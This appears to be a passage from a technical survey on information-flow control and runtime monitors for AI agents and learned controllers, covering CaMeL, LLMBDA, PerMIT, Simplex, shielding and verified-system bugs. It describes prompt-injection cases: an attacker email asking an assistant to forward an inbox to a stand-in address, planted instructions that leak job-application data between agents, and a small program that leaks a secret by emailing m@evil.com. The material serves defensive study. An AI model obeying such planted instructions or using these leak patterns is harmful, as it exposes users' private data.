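Each value's label records its sources and who may read it. A value computed from others inherits their sources. Before every tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short Python function that takes the labeled arguments and allows or denies the call. Here the policy for `send_email` requires a trusted recipient.

Suppose an attacker wrote the last email, giving Bob's address as `bob@mallory.example` and telling the assistant to forward the whole inbox there.

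| Step | Result | Sources in the label | Effect of the planted text |
|---|---|---|---|
| `get_last_email` | The attacker's email | The email | None yet |
| `ask_quarantined` | `bob@mallory.example` | The email, the quarantined model | The address is false |
| `send_email` | The policy denies the call or asks the user | The recipient comes from the email | The attacker gets nothing unless the user agrees |

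The order to forward the inbox has no effect because the program was complete before anyone opened the email and contains no such step. The false address does enter the program as a value, and only its label stops it.

If Bob had written the email himself, his real address would have the same label because it would still come from an untrusted source, and the policy would still stop the reminder or ask the user. A policy could accept addresses in the user's contact list, but an attacker could then choose which contact receives the message.

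CaMeL's policies check one call at a time, so they can't require something to happen later. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a security team whose agent must resolve or escalate every incident ticket before it finishes. The system converts the program into a finite set of states and checks every path through it before any tool runs. If a path breaks a rule, the privileged model receives that path and tries to repair the program. The conversion treats a loop as if it could run any number of times, so the check may reject a safe plan.

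### Benchmark results with and without policies

Most tests of CaMeL use AgentDojo, the benchmark also used in Agenra's trials. Its 97 ordinary tasks cover office work, banking, Slack and travel. The benchmark has 35 attack goals in total and pairs each task with every goal from the same setting.

$$
40\times14+16\times9+21\times5+20\times7=949\ \text{attacked cases}
$$

Debenedetti and colleagues reported that CaMeL completed 77% of the tasks, against 84% for an agent with no defence. Later tests produced much lower figures. *SecureClaw* (2026) ran CaMeL on the same 97 tasks and on an earlier set of 629 attacked cases. No attack succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks and 195 of the 629 attacked cases. The test compared CaMeL with the paper's own system and used an adapted version of CaMeL's code, so some of the shortfall may come from the adaptation.

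Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found another reason. They ran CaMeL three times on each of the 16 banking tasks, with its policies on and off.

| Model and setting | Tasks completed without an attack | Attacks that succeeded, in completed runs |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2, policies off | 32 of 48 | 1 of 240 |
| GPT-5.2, policies on | 18 of 48 | 0 of 231 |
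| MiMo-v2.5, policies off | 34 of 48 | 4 of 382 |
| MiMo-v2.5, policies on | 18 of 48 | 0 of 357 |

The fixed plan alone stops nearly every attack on this benchmark. In 97 of the 144 task-attack pairs, the attack needs a step that an ordinary plan for the task would never contain. The policies stop the few remaining attacks, but they also prevent nearly half of the tasks that would otherwise be completed. A success rate for CaMeL is therefore hard to interpret without knowing whether its policies were on.

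Because the plan is fixed in advance, the agent can't respond to surprises. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) studied agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen, and had the privileged model write long programs with branches for many possible screens. These agents kept at most 57% of the performance of leading agents. An attacker could also steer them into a harmful branch that was already in the plan, for example with an advertisement that looked like a cookie notice.

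### Where CaMeL loses a label

Debenedetti and colleagues left a formal proof about CaMeL to later work. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) warned that Python's exceptions, dynamic types and ability to inspect itself would make strong guarantees difficult, and recommended a purpose-built language. Garby and colleagues then found specific leaks, including a version of a flow that Fenton and Denning described in the 1970s. The following program shows this kind of flow. The customer's balance is secret, and everything else starts out public.

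```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

| | Balance above threshold | Balance below threshold |
|---|---|---|
| Third line | `tmp` becomes False, with a secret label | Skipped, so `tmp` stays True and public |
| Fourth line | Skipped, so `rich` stays True and public | `rich` becomes False and stays public |
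| Last line | Sends the email | Sends nothing |

CaMeL raises a variable's label only when it runs an assignment. Whether the fourth line runs depends on the secret, but when the balance is high the line doesn't run, so `rich` never gets a secret label. The last line then depends only on a public value, so the policy doesn't stop the email.

Other label trackers have similar problems. FIDES, a comparable system, deliberately doesn't follow secrets through branches. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) tested it on scenarios written to evaluate a rival tracker. FIDES caught only 17 of 40 implicit flows, yet it raised an alarm on 94 of 140 harmless cases.

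Labels can also disappear between agents. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) built a system of three CaMeL agents without policies. A user asked the coordinating agent to send Julie a summary of some job applications on Slack. A database agent fetched the records, in which the researchers had planted an instruction to email the data to an outsider. The coordinator put the summary into a message for the notification agent, which treated the whole message as its user's request. Although every agent had followed CaMeL's rules, the notification agent's privileged model read the planted instruction and wrote a program to carry it out.

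Their repair splits each message into an instruction, which may not depend on any tool's output, and variables that carry everything else. The variables keep their labels, and the receiving agent's privileged model can't read them. In a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of cases without CaMeL, 0.2% with separate CaMeL agents and none with the split messages, averaged over five models. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack even without CaMeL, so the benchmark is no longer very informative about the strongest models. The repair also uses CaMeL's interpreter, so it has the same flaw with skipped branches, as Peters-Gill and colleagues acknowledge.

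### LLMBDA: a labelled conversation

Garby and colleagues designed LLMBDA, a small programming language for agents. It has a machine-checked proof of noninterference and consists of functions, ordinary data and a few operations for interacting with a language model. A program can send a prompt, receive a reply, clear the conversation, or *fork* it, which means working in a temporary copy and then discarding the copy. The privileged and quarantined models no longer need a fixed place in the architecture, because a program can use a quarantined model by forking the conversation, clearing the copy and sending its prompt there.

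Labels may contain U for untrusted and S for secret. The conversation also has a label, which combines the labels of everything sent so far, and each reply inherits it. Once a program has sent the payroll file to the model, every later reply in that conversation is secret, whether or not it mentions pay. This rule is crude, but it is sound because it doesn't depend on working out which parts of a prompt influenced a reply. If the reply is code, the interpreter can run it under the same label.

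LLMBDA also stops a program that tries to change public state inside a branch that a secret selected. For example, a program can't add a line to a public conversation only if the salary exceeds 60,000. The same rule would stop the program with `tmp` and `rich` at its third line when the balance is high.

Stopping can itself reveal something, since the program would have continued with a lower balance. The theorem permits this leak but limits it. Because models choose their words at random, it compares probabilities. Let μ₁(r) and μ₂(r) be the probabilities that an observer receives the reply r when the secret has one value or another. The theorem guarantees that some ω satisfies:

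$$
\mu_1(r)\le\omega(r)\ \text{ and }\ \mu_2(r)\le\omega(r)\ \text{ for every } r,\qquad \sum_r \omega(r)\le 1
$$

Suppose the assistant from the payroll example may put either a full stop or an exclamation mark after "Three o'clock".

| Salary in the file | Full stop | Exclamation mark | No reply |
|---|---|---|---|
| 50,000 | 0.6 | 0.3 | 0.1 |
| 70,000 | 0.5 | 0.4 | 0.1 |

The larger numbers in the two reply columns, 0.6 and 0.4, add up to 1, so the theorem allows this. If the assistant always replied, the reply probabilities in each row would add up to 1, and the theorem would require the rows to be identical. In general, the two distributions can differ by no more than the average probability of no reply, which is 0.1 here.

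To prove this, Garby and colleagues define a second way of running programs, which skips each computation as soon as its label becomes invisible to the observer. All the differences between the two secrets are in the skipped computations, so the results are the same for both secrets and supply ω. The Lean proof covers every program in the language, including code that a model writes during a run. This takes the agent's plan out of the unverified host, where it would be with Keleusma.

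### What the proof assumes about the model

The theorem assumes that the probability of each model reply depends only on the text of the current conversation, but it assumes nothing about the quality or honesty of the replies. A hosted model that retains information about customers between conversations would break this assumption. A program could mention a secret in one conversation, clear that conversation, and get the secret back in another marked public. The same could happen if the hosting company's servers mixed up two customers' requests.

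The verified interpreter contacts the model through ordinary network code, which the proof replaces with an abstract source of replies. The prompt goes to the model provider's computers, but the theorem treats sending it as an internal step, not an output. A secret can therefore reach another company without violating noninterference. The CaMeL paper suggests running the quarantined model on the user's own machine, so that the privileged model's provider never receives the contents of emails or files.

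Garby and colleagues note another limitation of their model, that it includes all tools and data sources as part of the program. This suits a benchmark with a simulated bank, but a real bank's data can change between two calls, and nobody has yet extended the theorem to cover that.

### Endorsing a value without revealing it

An agent that never trusts anything it reads can't pay a bill from a file. LLMBDA therefore has an operator, `endorse`, that removes U from a label. If i is the integrity part of a label and s the secrecy part, then

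$$
\mathrm{endorse}:\ (i,s)\ \longmapsto\ (i',s)
$$

where i′ is the new integrity part. If a value has both U and S, endorsing it removes the U and leaves the S, so a tool that refuses secret arguments will still refuse it. A second theorem shows that secrets remain protected in every program that uses `endorse`, even when an attacker chooses all the untrusted data. Swapping the two parts gives an operator that declassifies secrets and leaves integrity protected. If one operator could weaken both, the theorem would guarantee nothing.

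The program gives up the integrity guarantee. Garby and colleagues tested this with Randori, an agent written in LLMBDA. Randori tries out its plan on invented data until the plan runs without errors, because error messages from real data would make later versions of the plan untrusted. In the banking tests, it completed 36 of 48 tasks with GPT-5.2, and attackers succeeded in 2 of 1,296 runs across three models. Both successful attacks involved a request to make whatever payment a certain file specified. The attacker had replaced the file, and the plan endorsed its contents.

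Without `endorse`, Randori would have blocked those two payments. But it completed only 30 tasks instead of 36 with one model and 26 instead of 31 with another, partly because it could no longer pay legitimate bills from files. These tests show that much of the usefulness comes from deliberate exceptions to the labels. They don't show which agent is better, because Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies and the margins of error are around 20 points.

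### Memory between sessions

An agent with a long-term memory can save a planted instruction today and act on it months later. If the instruction's label disappears when the session ends, the agent later reads the instruction as part of its own notes. *PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026) presents a memory design that keeps the distinction between trusted and untrusted content.

The protected model in PerMIT can read only what the user typed or explicitly confirmed. Tool output stays in the store, and the model receives a handle to it. A quarantined model can search the store and also returns handles. Suppose a web page plants a false address for the user's accountant in June, and in August the user asks the agent to send the accountant some invoices. The agent finds the address in its memory and passes the handle to the email tool. PerMIT then pauses and displays the exact address,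 its source and the user's original request.

Jiang and colleagues proved two theorems and checked the core of both in Lean. One establishes that every argument to a sensitive tool is either something the user typed or something the user confirmed for that tool, byte for byte. The other compares two runs, ρ₁ and ρ₂, in which the user types the same things but the untrusted memories differ:

$$
\mathrm{Display}(\rho_1)=\mathrm{Display}(\rho_2)\ \Rightarrow\ \mathrm{Behaviour}(\rho_1)=\mathrm{Behaviour}(\rho_2)
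$$

Display is everything PerMIT showed at its confirmation step, together with the decisions. If Display and the random choices are the same in both runs, the agent behaves the same way, so untrusted memories can influence it only through what PerMIT displayed. The agent may still change its plan after each confirmation, which a CaMeL agent can't do. Jiang and colleagues cite AgentDyn, a benchmark of changing tasks, on which CaMeL completed none of them.

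The theorems assume that whoever confirms a value means to authorise it. The confirmer may be another language model, or a person, who may click through the prompt as Anthropic's testers did. A confirmation also never expires and isn't tied to a purpose. If the user approves the accountant's address for the invoices, the agent can later email medical records to the same address without asking again. In a shared version of PerMIT, once enough users have confirmed an entry for a tool, other users' agents can use it without asking them.

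### What, who, where and when

Endorsement and declassification both make exceptions to a rule, and those exceptions need rules too. *Information-Flow Control, A Deep Dive with Keleusma* recommends four questions that Sabelfeld and Sands (2009) used to classify declassification. The questions apply equally well to endorsement.

| Question | Example of a limit |
|---|---|
| What may the program release? | An LLMBDA program accepts one of eight tags from an untrusted email, which is at most three bits |
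| Who controls the release? | In PerMIT, only the person or model at the confirmation step |
| Where may it happen? | In Keleusma, only at the operator `declassify` |
| When, or how often? | In Agenra, once per approval |

A limit on one of these doesn't replace limits on the others. Keleusma, for example, limits where a program may release a value but not what it releases.

It is hard to determine who controls a release, because an attacker may influence it without performing it. Suppose an assistant is allowed to send a contractor one field from an employee's file, normally the phone extension, and it takes the name of the field from the contractor's web page. If that name is "salary", the assistant releases the salary at the permitted place and to the permitted person.

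Zdancewic and Myers (2001) called a system *robust* if an attacker who interferes with it learns no more than one who only watches. When the secret is s, let R(s) be the set of secrets that the watcher can't rule out, and let Rₐ(s) be the set that someone who carries out attack a can't rule out.

$$
\text{robust}\iff R(s)\subseteq R_a(s)\ \text{ for every secret } s \text{ and every attack } a
$$

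The assistant isn't robust, because the attack rules out nearly all the possible salaries, while watching alone would have ruled out none. To repair it, the programmer must ensure that only trusted data decides whether a release happens and what it contains. Settling the plan in advance isn't enough, since a CaMeL program may contain two permitted releases and let an untrusted email choose between them. Garby and colleagues describe a related restriction for endorsement, which prevents endorsed code from creating code with further endorsements.

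### Twenty harmless answers

A company gives each customer a secret number from 0 to 1,048,575, written as 20 binary digits. When asked about a customer's number, the company's assistant may only answer whether a particular digit is 1. Any single answer leaves 524,288 possible numbers, so a reviewer might reasonably approve it.

| Answers received | Numbers that the latest answer alone leaves | Numbers that all the answers leave |
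|---|---|---|
| 1 | 524,288 | 524,288 |
| 2 | 524,288 | 262,144 |
| 10 | 524,288 | 1,024 |
| 20 | 524,288 | 1 |

After twenty answers, the outsider knows the number. Every release was of the permitted kind, at the permitted place and to a permitted person, so a theorem that allows each one also allows all twenty. CaMeL has an unintended version of this problem because its interpreter runs inside an ordinary Python loop that retries after a failure. A program can make a secret digit determine whether a policy blocks it, and the loop can then test one digit after another.

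A kernel can prevent this by keeping a budget. If the i-th release has nᵢ possible values, it reveals at most log₂ nᵢ bits, and the kernel enforces

$$
\sum_i \log_2 n_i \le B
$$

With B = 10, the kernel would refuse the eleventh question, and 1,024 possible numbers would remain. It has to count every question against the budget regardless of the answer, because if it refused only when an answer would reveal too much, the refusal would reveal information too. Each secret needs a single budget shared by all users, since otherwise twenty people could ask one question each and combine the answers. The count must also survive restarts. Such a budget eventually stops honest users as well. A bank that confirms account numbers all day can't limit each account to ten bits for life, so in practice designers let the budget refill and accept a slow leak.

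### After the value has left

CaMeL can check that Bob is allowed to read a document before emailing it to him, but once the email reaches his mail server, the document is an ordinary file without a label. The label is also lost when a person reads the text on a screen. If the agent calls another company's service, the value enters that company's databases, where the company's staff and agents may use it. Peters-Gill and colleagues could keep labels on values that passed between agents only because all the agents ran the same interpreter.

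*Usage control* is an attempt to govern this stage. In their UCON model (2004), Park and Sandhu extended access control beyond the opening of a file to the whole time it is in use. A decision may depend on who the user is, duties such as accepting a licence, and circumstances such as the time or place. The system can check again during use and withdraw permission, and using the data can change what the user may do next. For instance, the company could let Bob open a payroll summary on a work laptop up to three times before Friday, but not copy or forward it.

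Enforcing these rules on Bob's laptop in effect requires a second kernel, on a machine whose owner may want to defeat it. The summary must arrive encrypted, and only a program that enforces the rules may hold the key. That program must mediate every attempt to read, copy or print the text, and it needs a clock and a counter that Bob can't set back. The sender also needs attestation that the laptop is running this program.

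If the recipient is another AI agent, that kernel must also track the summary through the agent's conversations and memory, roughly as LLMBDA and PerMIT do. If the recipient is a person, the kernel can block copying and screenshots, but Bob can still photograph the screen.

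## Simplex and shielding: a core that takes over instead of refusing

Most of the kernels described so far protect people by refusing forbidden actions. PocketFlow's loop emits no effect for such an action, and Mashin's runtime stops the program that requested it. This suits an email assistant, where inaction does little harm.

Refusing a command is sometimes not enough to prevent harm, so the kernel needs a safe action of its own, such as braking a car or reversing a debit. If a car is travelling at 20 metres per second towards a stationary lorry, rejecting a command to accelerate won't prevent the collision. Office software can have the same problem. If an agent moves money by debiting one account and then crediting another, a kernel that allows the debit but refuses the credit leaves the money missing from both accounts.

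### The Simplex architecture

Lui Sha described a design for such cases, the *Simplex architecture*, in a 2001 paper. Crenshaw (2008) summarises it as a way to combine two algorithms so that a system keeps the safety of one and gains the features of the other. A complex controller runs the machine most of the time. A monitor watches the machine's state and, if necessary, hands control to a simple, verified backup. The complex controller belongs to the host, while the monitor and the backup make up the kernel. According to *The Use of the Simplex Architecture to Enhance Safety* (2025), engineers originally wanted Simplex for testing new controllers on safety-critical equipment and for updating control software while it was running.

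Sorting a list is a simple example. A complex new routine sorts the list, and a short verified program checks that the result contains the same items in the right order. If the check fails, a slow but verified routine sorts the original list, so the final list is correct however bad the new routine is.

An alternative is to build several different programs and hope that they don't all fail together. In *Using Simplicity to Control Complexity*, a set of slides on Sha's paper, Foo reports that splitting a development budget among them can make a system more or less reliable, depending on the architecture. A simple, reliable core for the critical functions matters more.

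### When the backup can still save the car

A moving car can't wait for a check the way a list can, so the monitor has to hand control to the backup while the backup can still prevent a crash. Let R be a set of states that the backup can handle, and T the longest time between two decisions by the monitor.

$$
\begin{aligned}
&\text{every state in } R \text{ is safe}\\
&\text{from any state in } R,\ \text{the backup keeps the system in } R\\
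&\text{the monitor allows action } a \text{ only if the system stays in } R \text{ for the next } T \text{ seconds under } a
\end{aligned}
$$

A system that starts in R never leaves it, because in each period the monitor either allows an action that keeps it there or runs the backup. Checking that the present state is safe isn't enough. A car travelling at 20 m/s one metre from the lorry hasn't crashed yet, but it can't brake in time to avoid a collision.

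Suppose the car can brake at 5 m/s² and accelerate at 2 m/s², the monitor acts every 0.5 seconds, and the lorry is 50 metres ahead. The car needs v²/10 metres to stop from speed v, which is 40 metres at 20 m/s.

| Action for the next 0.5 s | Distance covered | Speed afterwards | Distance to stop from there | Total |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Accelerate | 10.25 m | 21 m/s | 44.1 m | 54.35 m |
| Keep the same speed | 10 m | 20 m/s | 40 m | 50 m |
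| Brake | 9.375 m | 17.5 m/s | 30.625 m | 40 m |

The monitor must brake now, although the car could still stop 10 metres short of the lorry. If the monitor allows another half second of acceleration, the car will hit the lorry at about 6.6 m/s, even if it then brakes fully. If the car held its speed for that half second before braking fully, it would stop exactly at the lorry's bumper.

A faster monitor could give the complex controller more freedom. If it acted every 0.1 seconds, the accelerating car would need only 42.8 metres. If the designer's estimate of R is too small, the monitor takes over when there is no danger, and an estimate that is too large is unsafe.

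In *Context-dependent Runtime Construction of Safe Regions of Attraction from Design-Time Identification*, Jäger, Friedrich and colleagues (2026) try to reduce unnecessary takeovers on a wheeled robot that follows a path. They do the heavy calculations in advance for different conditions. While the robot is moving, the monitor assembles the safe region for the current conditions and can choose among several backups. They tested the design in two kinds of simulation and on a physical robot, where it protected a controller trained by imitation. The monitor took 0.028 milliseconds on average and 4.13 milliseconds at worst, less than a tenth of the time between control decisions.

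### Shielding learned controllers

In *reinforcement learning*, a controller learns by trying actions and receiving rewards. It may discover that an action is bad only by trying it, which is unacceptable on a real road. *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding* (2017), by Alshiekh and colleagues, addresses this with a *shield*, a program that blocks unsafe actions during and after training. The designer supplies a simplified model of the environment and a formal safety rule, and an algorithm builds the shield from them. The shield doesn't depend on how the controller works internally. In the paper's experiments, controllers with a shield performed at least as well as those without one, and usually learned better.

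A shield can remove the unsafe actions and let the learner choose among the rest, instead of taking over completely. With the lorry 50 metres ahead, only braking would remain, but at 52 metres the learner could also keep its speed.

Some shields tolerate a small risk. *Easy-to-Use Shielding for Reinforcement Learning* (2026) describes a tool tested on a slippery grid with lava. For each position and action, the tool calculates the lowest achievable probability that the agent eventually falls in, and it blocks the action if that probability exceeds a threshold. The developers set the threshold at 1% or 0.1%, which determines how close to the lava the agent may go.

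Such a threshold limits the risk of each decision, but not the total risk across a sequence of decisions. If an agent takes ten steps that each carry a 0.5% risk, every step passes the 1% threshold, but the total risk is nearly 5%. Limiting the total requires a budget, as with the twenty harmless answers about a secret number.

### Monitors derived from proofs

A person who writes a monitor by hand may leave out a condition that the safety proof needs. Mitsch and Platzer (2016), in *ModelPlex*, avoid this by deriving the monitor from the verified model, with a proof that passing the check preserves the safety result. Their running example is a water tank that must not overflow. The tank holds at most m litres and currently contains x. A controller chooses the flow f, in litres per second, and will choose again within ε seconds. Mitsch and Platzer prove that the tank never overflows if every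 choice satisfies

$$
-1\ \le\ f\ \le\ \frac{m-x}{\varepsilon}
$$

ModelPlex turns this condition into a check that runs before the valve moves. If a ten-litre tank contains 9.8 litres and the controller runs every half second, the check allows an inflow of up to 0.4 litres per second. If a neural network outputs 0.7, the fallback takes over.

ModelPlex also compares the tank with the model. At 0.4 litres per second, the level should rise by 0.2 litres in half a second. If it rises by 0.3, somebody may have opened another pipe, and the proof no longer applies. The fallback then starts, but it may be too late. *Verified Runtime Validation for Partially Observable Hybrid Systems* (2018) proves recovery for actions that the system can discard or undo before they have a lasting physical effect. This covers a valve command that the monitor can still cancel, but not water that has already flowed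 into the tank.

Mitsch and Platzer guarantee safety after reality departs from the model only if there is a limit on how far it can depart. Without such a limit, they write, safety guarantees are impossible.

The car example shows how a small error in the model can defeat a correct monitor. Suppose the lorry is 55 metres ahead and a wet road has reduced the braking to 4 m/s². The monitor still uses 5, so it calculates that the car can accelerate for another half second and stop within 54.35 metres, and it allows the acceleration. The car actually needs 65.4 metres and hits the lorry at about 9 m/s, even though the monitor and the backup both met their specifications.

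Other parts of the trusted computing base are easier to verify than the road. *VeriPhy* (Bohrer, Tan and colleagues, 2018) carries the proof from the model down to the program that the machine runs, and uses one prover to check another. The paper's remaining assumption is that the model faithfully represents the physical environment.

### A neural network on the highway

*Verification of Autonomous Neural Car Control with KeYmaera X* (Prebet, Teuber and Platzer, 2025) applies these methods to a simulated car on a single-lane highway. A neural network chooses whether to brake, keep its speed or accelerate. The rule resembles the lorry calculation, except that the vehicle in front is also moving. It assumes that the other car brakes as hard as possible and that the network's car can brake only at its guaranteed minimum. The fallback brakes if the other car is ahead and accelerates if it is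 behind.

The team used the theorem prover KeYmaera X to show that a car obeying the rule never hits the other car, however long the trip. They then tested a network from 1,000 starting positions in which a crash was avoidable. In these tests, the car in front made an emergency stop, and the network's car had weak brakes.

| Protection | Crashes in 1,000 runs | Average reward |
|---|---|---|
| None | 996 | 5.44 |
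| Monitor that replaces an unsafe action with the fallback | 0 | 16.47 |
| Shield that picks the network's preferred safe action | 0 | 16.47 |

The network did so badly because, during its training, cars in front rarely braked hard and its own brakes always worked at full strength. The result is strong evidence that a small kernel can protect a poor controller, but the theorem concerns only one other car, so it doesn't cover a car that brakes for the vehicle ahead and gets hit from behind. The test also used a Python version of the monitor, without VeriPhy's guarantees about the compiled program. And the monitor needs correct positions, which on a real road come from cameras and other sensors. *Synergistic Simplex* (2026) extends Simplex to perception, where a learned system may fail to notice the lorry.

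Prebet and colleagues also found that the simulator didn't match its written specification. By default, the "brake" action lowered the car's target speed by 5 m/s, so a car travelling at 10 m/s with a target of 20 would speed up towards the new target of 15. They had to train a new network with direct control of the brakes before their proof could apply.

They then trained an improved network on more emergency stops. It had no crashes in 1,000 tests without a monitor. However, a tool for verifying neural networks found 11,059 regions of unsafe behaviour, and simulations based on those regions produced thousands of crashes. A few were caused by the simulator's coarse time steps. These happened even when the car braked at once, and they disappeared with finer steps. Almost all the crashes caused by the network remained with the finer steps.

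The monitor is worth keeping even when a network tests well. *Assuring Learning-Enabled Cyber-Physical Systems with Foundation Models* (2026) recommends Simplex for systems with learned parts because complete verification of realistic systems of this kind is not yet feasible.

### Guaranteed safe AI

*Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple et al., 2024) proposes applying the same kind of reasoning to AI systems in general, using three components: a *world model* that describes how the AI's actions affect its environment, a *safety specification* that defines which effects are acceptable, and a *verifier* that establishes that the system meets the specification in the world model. For the highway car, these are the equations of motion, the rule against collisions, and KeYmaera X.

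The guarantee may be a proof or a limit on the probability of harm. When the designer isn't sure which model is right, the guarantee can cover a set of models.

$$
\Pr_W(\text{the system violates the specification})\ \le\ \delta\qquad\text{for every world model } W \text{ in the set}
$$

If the set includes an accurate model of the real environment, the limit δ also holds there. The verifier can't establish that it does.

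The main objection is that nobody has an adequate model of the open-ended settings in which people use AI. A few equations describe a car's motion, but none predict how a customer will react to an email or what the customer's colleagues will do next. It is also unclear what the backup should do. An assistant halfway through a negotiation has no equivalent of braking, since silence may cause the deal to collapse.

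Dalrymple and colleagues reply that the world model needn't be complete, because the detail it needs depends on the specification and on where people will use the system. The braking calculation doesn't need the colour of the lorry. Checking a rule that payroll data must not leave the company requires a model of the company's software, but not of its customers' feelings. Where the effects are uncertain, the designer can make the model cautious by including more effects than could really occur.

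These replies work well for narrow specifications but less well when the specification concerns how words affect people. A cautious model would have to include the possibility that almost any email could cause almost any reaction, so the verifier could not approve any email. Comparing the world with the model during use would help only if the system detected the mismatch in time and still had a safe action available. A general assistant often has neither a limit on the mismatch nor a reliable backup, so for now the proposal is much more convincing for cars, power grids and software than for open-ended conversation.

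### ARIA's Safeguarded AI programme

The largest attempt to put the proposal into practice is probably Safeguarded AI, a £59 million programme run by the UK government's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA). Dalrymple was its first director. The original plan was to show that AI could control real systems under mathematical guarantees, and so build agreement that powerful AI should act only through a verifiable "gatekeeper". The University of Oxford's *Oxford researchers awarded ARIA funding to develop safety-first AI* (April 2025) announced that nine British teams would work on quantitative safety guarantees for the programme.

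In November 2025, ARIA cancelled the part of the plan that would have developed specialised AI models. Dalrymple explained in ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025) that general models were improving faster than he had expected and would soon have many of the necessary abilities anyway. As programme director, Ammann published a revised plan, *Safeguarded AI*, in May 2026. It moves the £18 million set aside for those models to software tools for mathematical modelling and proof. She also writes that timely international agreement on a gatekeeper has become less likely.

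ARIA's Safeguarded AI programme has shifted its applications towards cybersecurity. According to the programme's web page, the agency dropped a planned second round of funding for systems that control physical processes, although existing projects will run to completion. It is now spending £22 million on eight projects that test whether AI can help prove software and hardware secure, including at least one on containing AI agents. The programme is due to end in late 2027.

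ARIA attributes these changes to the speed of AI progress, not to the difficulty of modelling the world, though the new focus makes modelling easier because a program's environment consists largely of a processor and other programs. Ammann still lists a main controller with a runtime monitor and a verified backup among the possible applications, but the programme has not yet demonstrated such a system at the scale it originally planned.

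## Testing verified systems: where the bugs were found

Most of the evidence about verified systems comes from the people who built them. Tests by outsiders are a useful check because they exercise the whole system, including the parts that a proof assumes are correct.

*An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems* (Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues, 2017) examined three research prototypes that keep copies of data on several servers. IronFleet and Verdi are supposed to make the servers behave like a single machine. Chapar is supposed to provide a weaker guarantee, roughly that nobody sees an effect before its cause. The researchers read the code, tried out faults known from other systems, and ran the servers under a *fuzzer*, a program that generates random or damaged inputs. This one duplicated and reordered network messages and made disk operations fail.

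They found 16 bugs.

| Place | Bugs | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Shim, the code that joins the proved part to the network and the disk | 11 | Verdi erased its old snapshot of the data before safely writing the new one, so a crash in between lost data |
| Specification | 2 | IronFleet's specification allowed a server to carry out the same request twice |
| Verification tools | 3 | A build script reported success after the prover had crashed |

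Nine of the 11 shim bugs made servers crash or hang. None were in IronFleet, which had the least unverified code.

The researchers also spent more than eight months looking for mistakes in the protocols the servers use to reach agreement, which are notoriously hard to get right. The proofs covered these protocols, and the researchers found no mistakes in them. A year of bug reports from four unverified systems contained 12 such mistakes, although those systems had many more features and users.

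IronFleet's server filtered out repeated requests, but its specification didn't require this. Fonseca and colleagues disabled the filter by changing seven lines, and the program still passed verification. The developers already knew about the omission and didn't consider it a bug.

More alarmingly, the build script would have passed any program when the prover crashed. The script searched the verifier's output for a line giving the number of errors and stopped reading there. After a crash, the verifier still printed that line, reporting no errors, and then a second message that the prover had died. The actual crash came from a packaging mistake, a 64-bit prover shipped with 32-bit libraries.

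### A correct function that crashed the server

One of the 11 shim bugs appeared in code that Verdi's tools had generated from a proved function. When a replica falls behind, the leading server uses this function to collect the log entries that the replica has missed. In simplified form:

```
1  missing(entries, i):
2      if entries is empty, return []
3      e = first entry; rest = all the others
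4      if e.index > i, return e followed by missing(rest, i)
5      otherwise, return []
```

The log runs from newest to oldest, and i is the newest entry the replica has. Line 2 handles the end of the log, and line 3 takes the newest remaining entry. Line 4 keeps that entry if the replica lacks it, then applies the function to the rest. Line 5 stops at the first entry the replica already has, since the remaining entries are older.

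Suppose the log contains entries 5 to 1 and the replica has everything up to 2.

| Call | Entry examined | Line that applies | Unfinished calls |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 5 | 4 | 1 |
| 2 | 4 | 4 | 2 |
| 3 | 3 | 4 | 3 |
| 4 | 2 | 5 | 3 |

The fourth call returns an empty list. The three unfinished calls then add 3, 4 and 5 in turn, giving the correct answer, [5, 4, 3]. By induction on the length of the log, one can prove that

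$$
\mathrm{missing}(L,i)=\text{the entries of } L \text{ with index greater than } i,\ \text{in order}
$$

for every log L that runs from newest to oldest. This is true for a log of any length, because a mathematical function can't run out of memory. The program generated from it can. It keeps each unfinished call on the stack, an area of memory with a fixed limit, and a replica that is n entries behind causes n unfinished calls. When a replica had fallen more than 500,000 requests behind, the stack overflowed and the leader crashed. The replica could then crash each new leader in the same way, until the whole system was down.

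Even that would not contradict Verdi's main theorem, which is a safety property, because servers that are down return no wrong answers. Fonseca and colleagues thought the bug would be hard to fix because the proof provided no way to reason about stack use. A crude resource check can catch a fault that a much deeper correctness proof misses. Keleusma's verifier, for example, would have rejected the function because it forbids recursion and computes a memory limit in advance.

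### CompCert's proved and unproved parts

CompCert is a C compiler with a machine-checked proof that its main stages preserve the meaning of a program. In *Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers*, Yang, Chen and colleagues (2011) tested it and ten other compilers with Csmith, a tool that generates random C programs. They compiled each program with several compilers and compared the results. If two results differed, at least one compiler was wrong, so they didn't need to know the right answer beforehand. Over three years they reported more than 325 bugs, and every compiler they tested both crashed and silently produced wrong code.

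Six of CompCert's wrong-code bugs were in its front end, which the proof didn't cover at the time. One affected this expression:

```
-1 <= (1 && x)
```

The part in brackets is always 0 or 1, so the comparison is true and the result should be 1, but the code CompCert produced returned 0. Two more bugs came from its formal description of the PowerPC processor, which omitted the 16-bit limit on a field in an instruction. CompCert therefore generated instructions containing numbers that were too large and relied on the next tool in the chain to reject them, which it did. The team also found a few crashes.

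Yang and colleagues designed Csmith to stress compilers' optimising stages, and it found many bugs in those stages of other compilers. After about six years of processor time, they had found no wrong-code bugs in CompCert's proved optimising stages. This is probably the best evidence that proofs prevent bugs, because the tests targeted the proved part. CompCert's main developer later extended the proof to cover some of the front end.

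### Recent tests

AI agents can now write both a program and its proof. Lean (2026) reports that a general-purpose AI rewrote zlib, a widely used compression library, in Lean, passed its test suite and proved the code correct. In April 2026, a main theorem about the result, lean-zip, was

$$
\mathrm{decompress}(\mathrm{compress}(d))=d\qquad\text{for all data } d \text{ under one gigabyte}
$$

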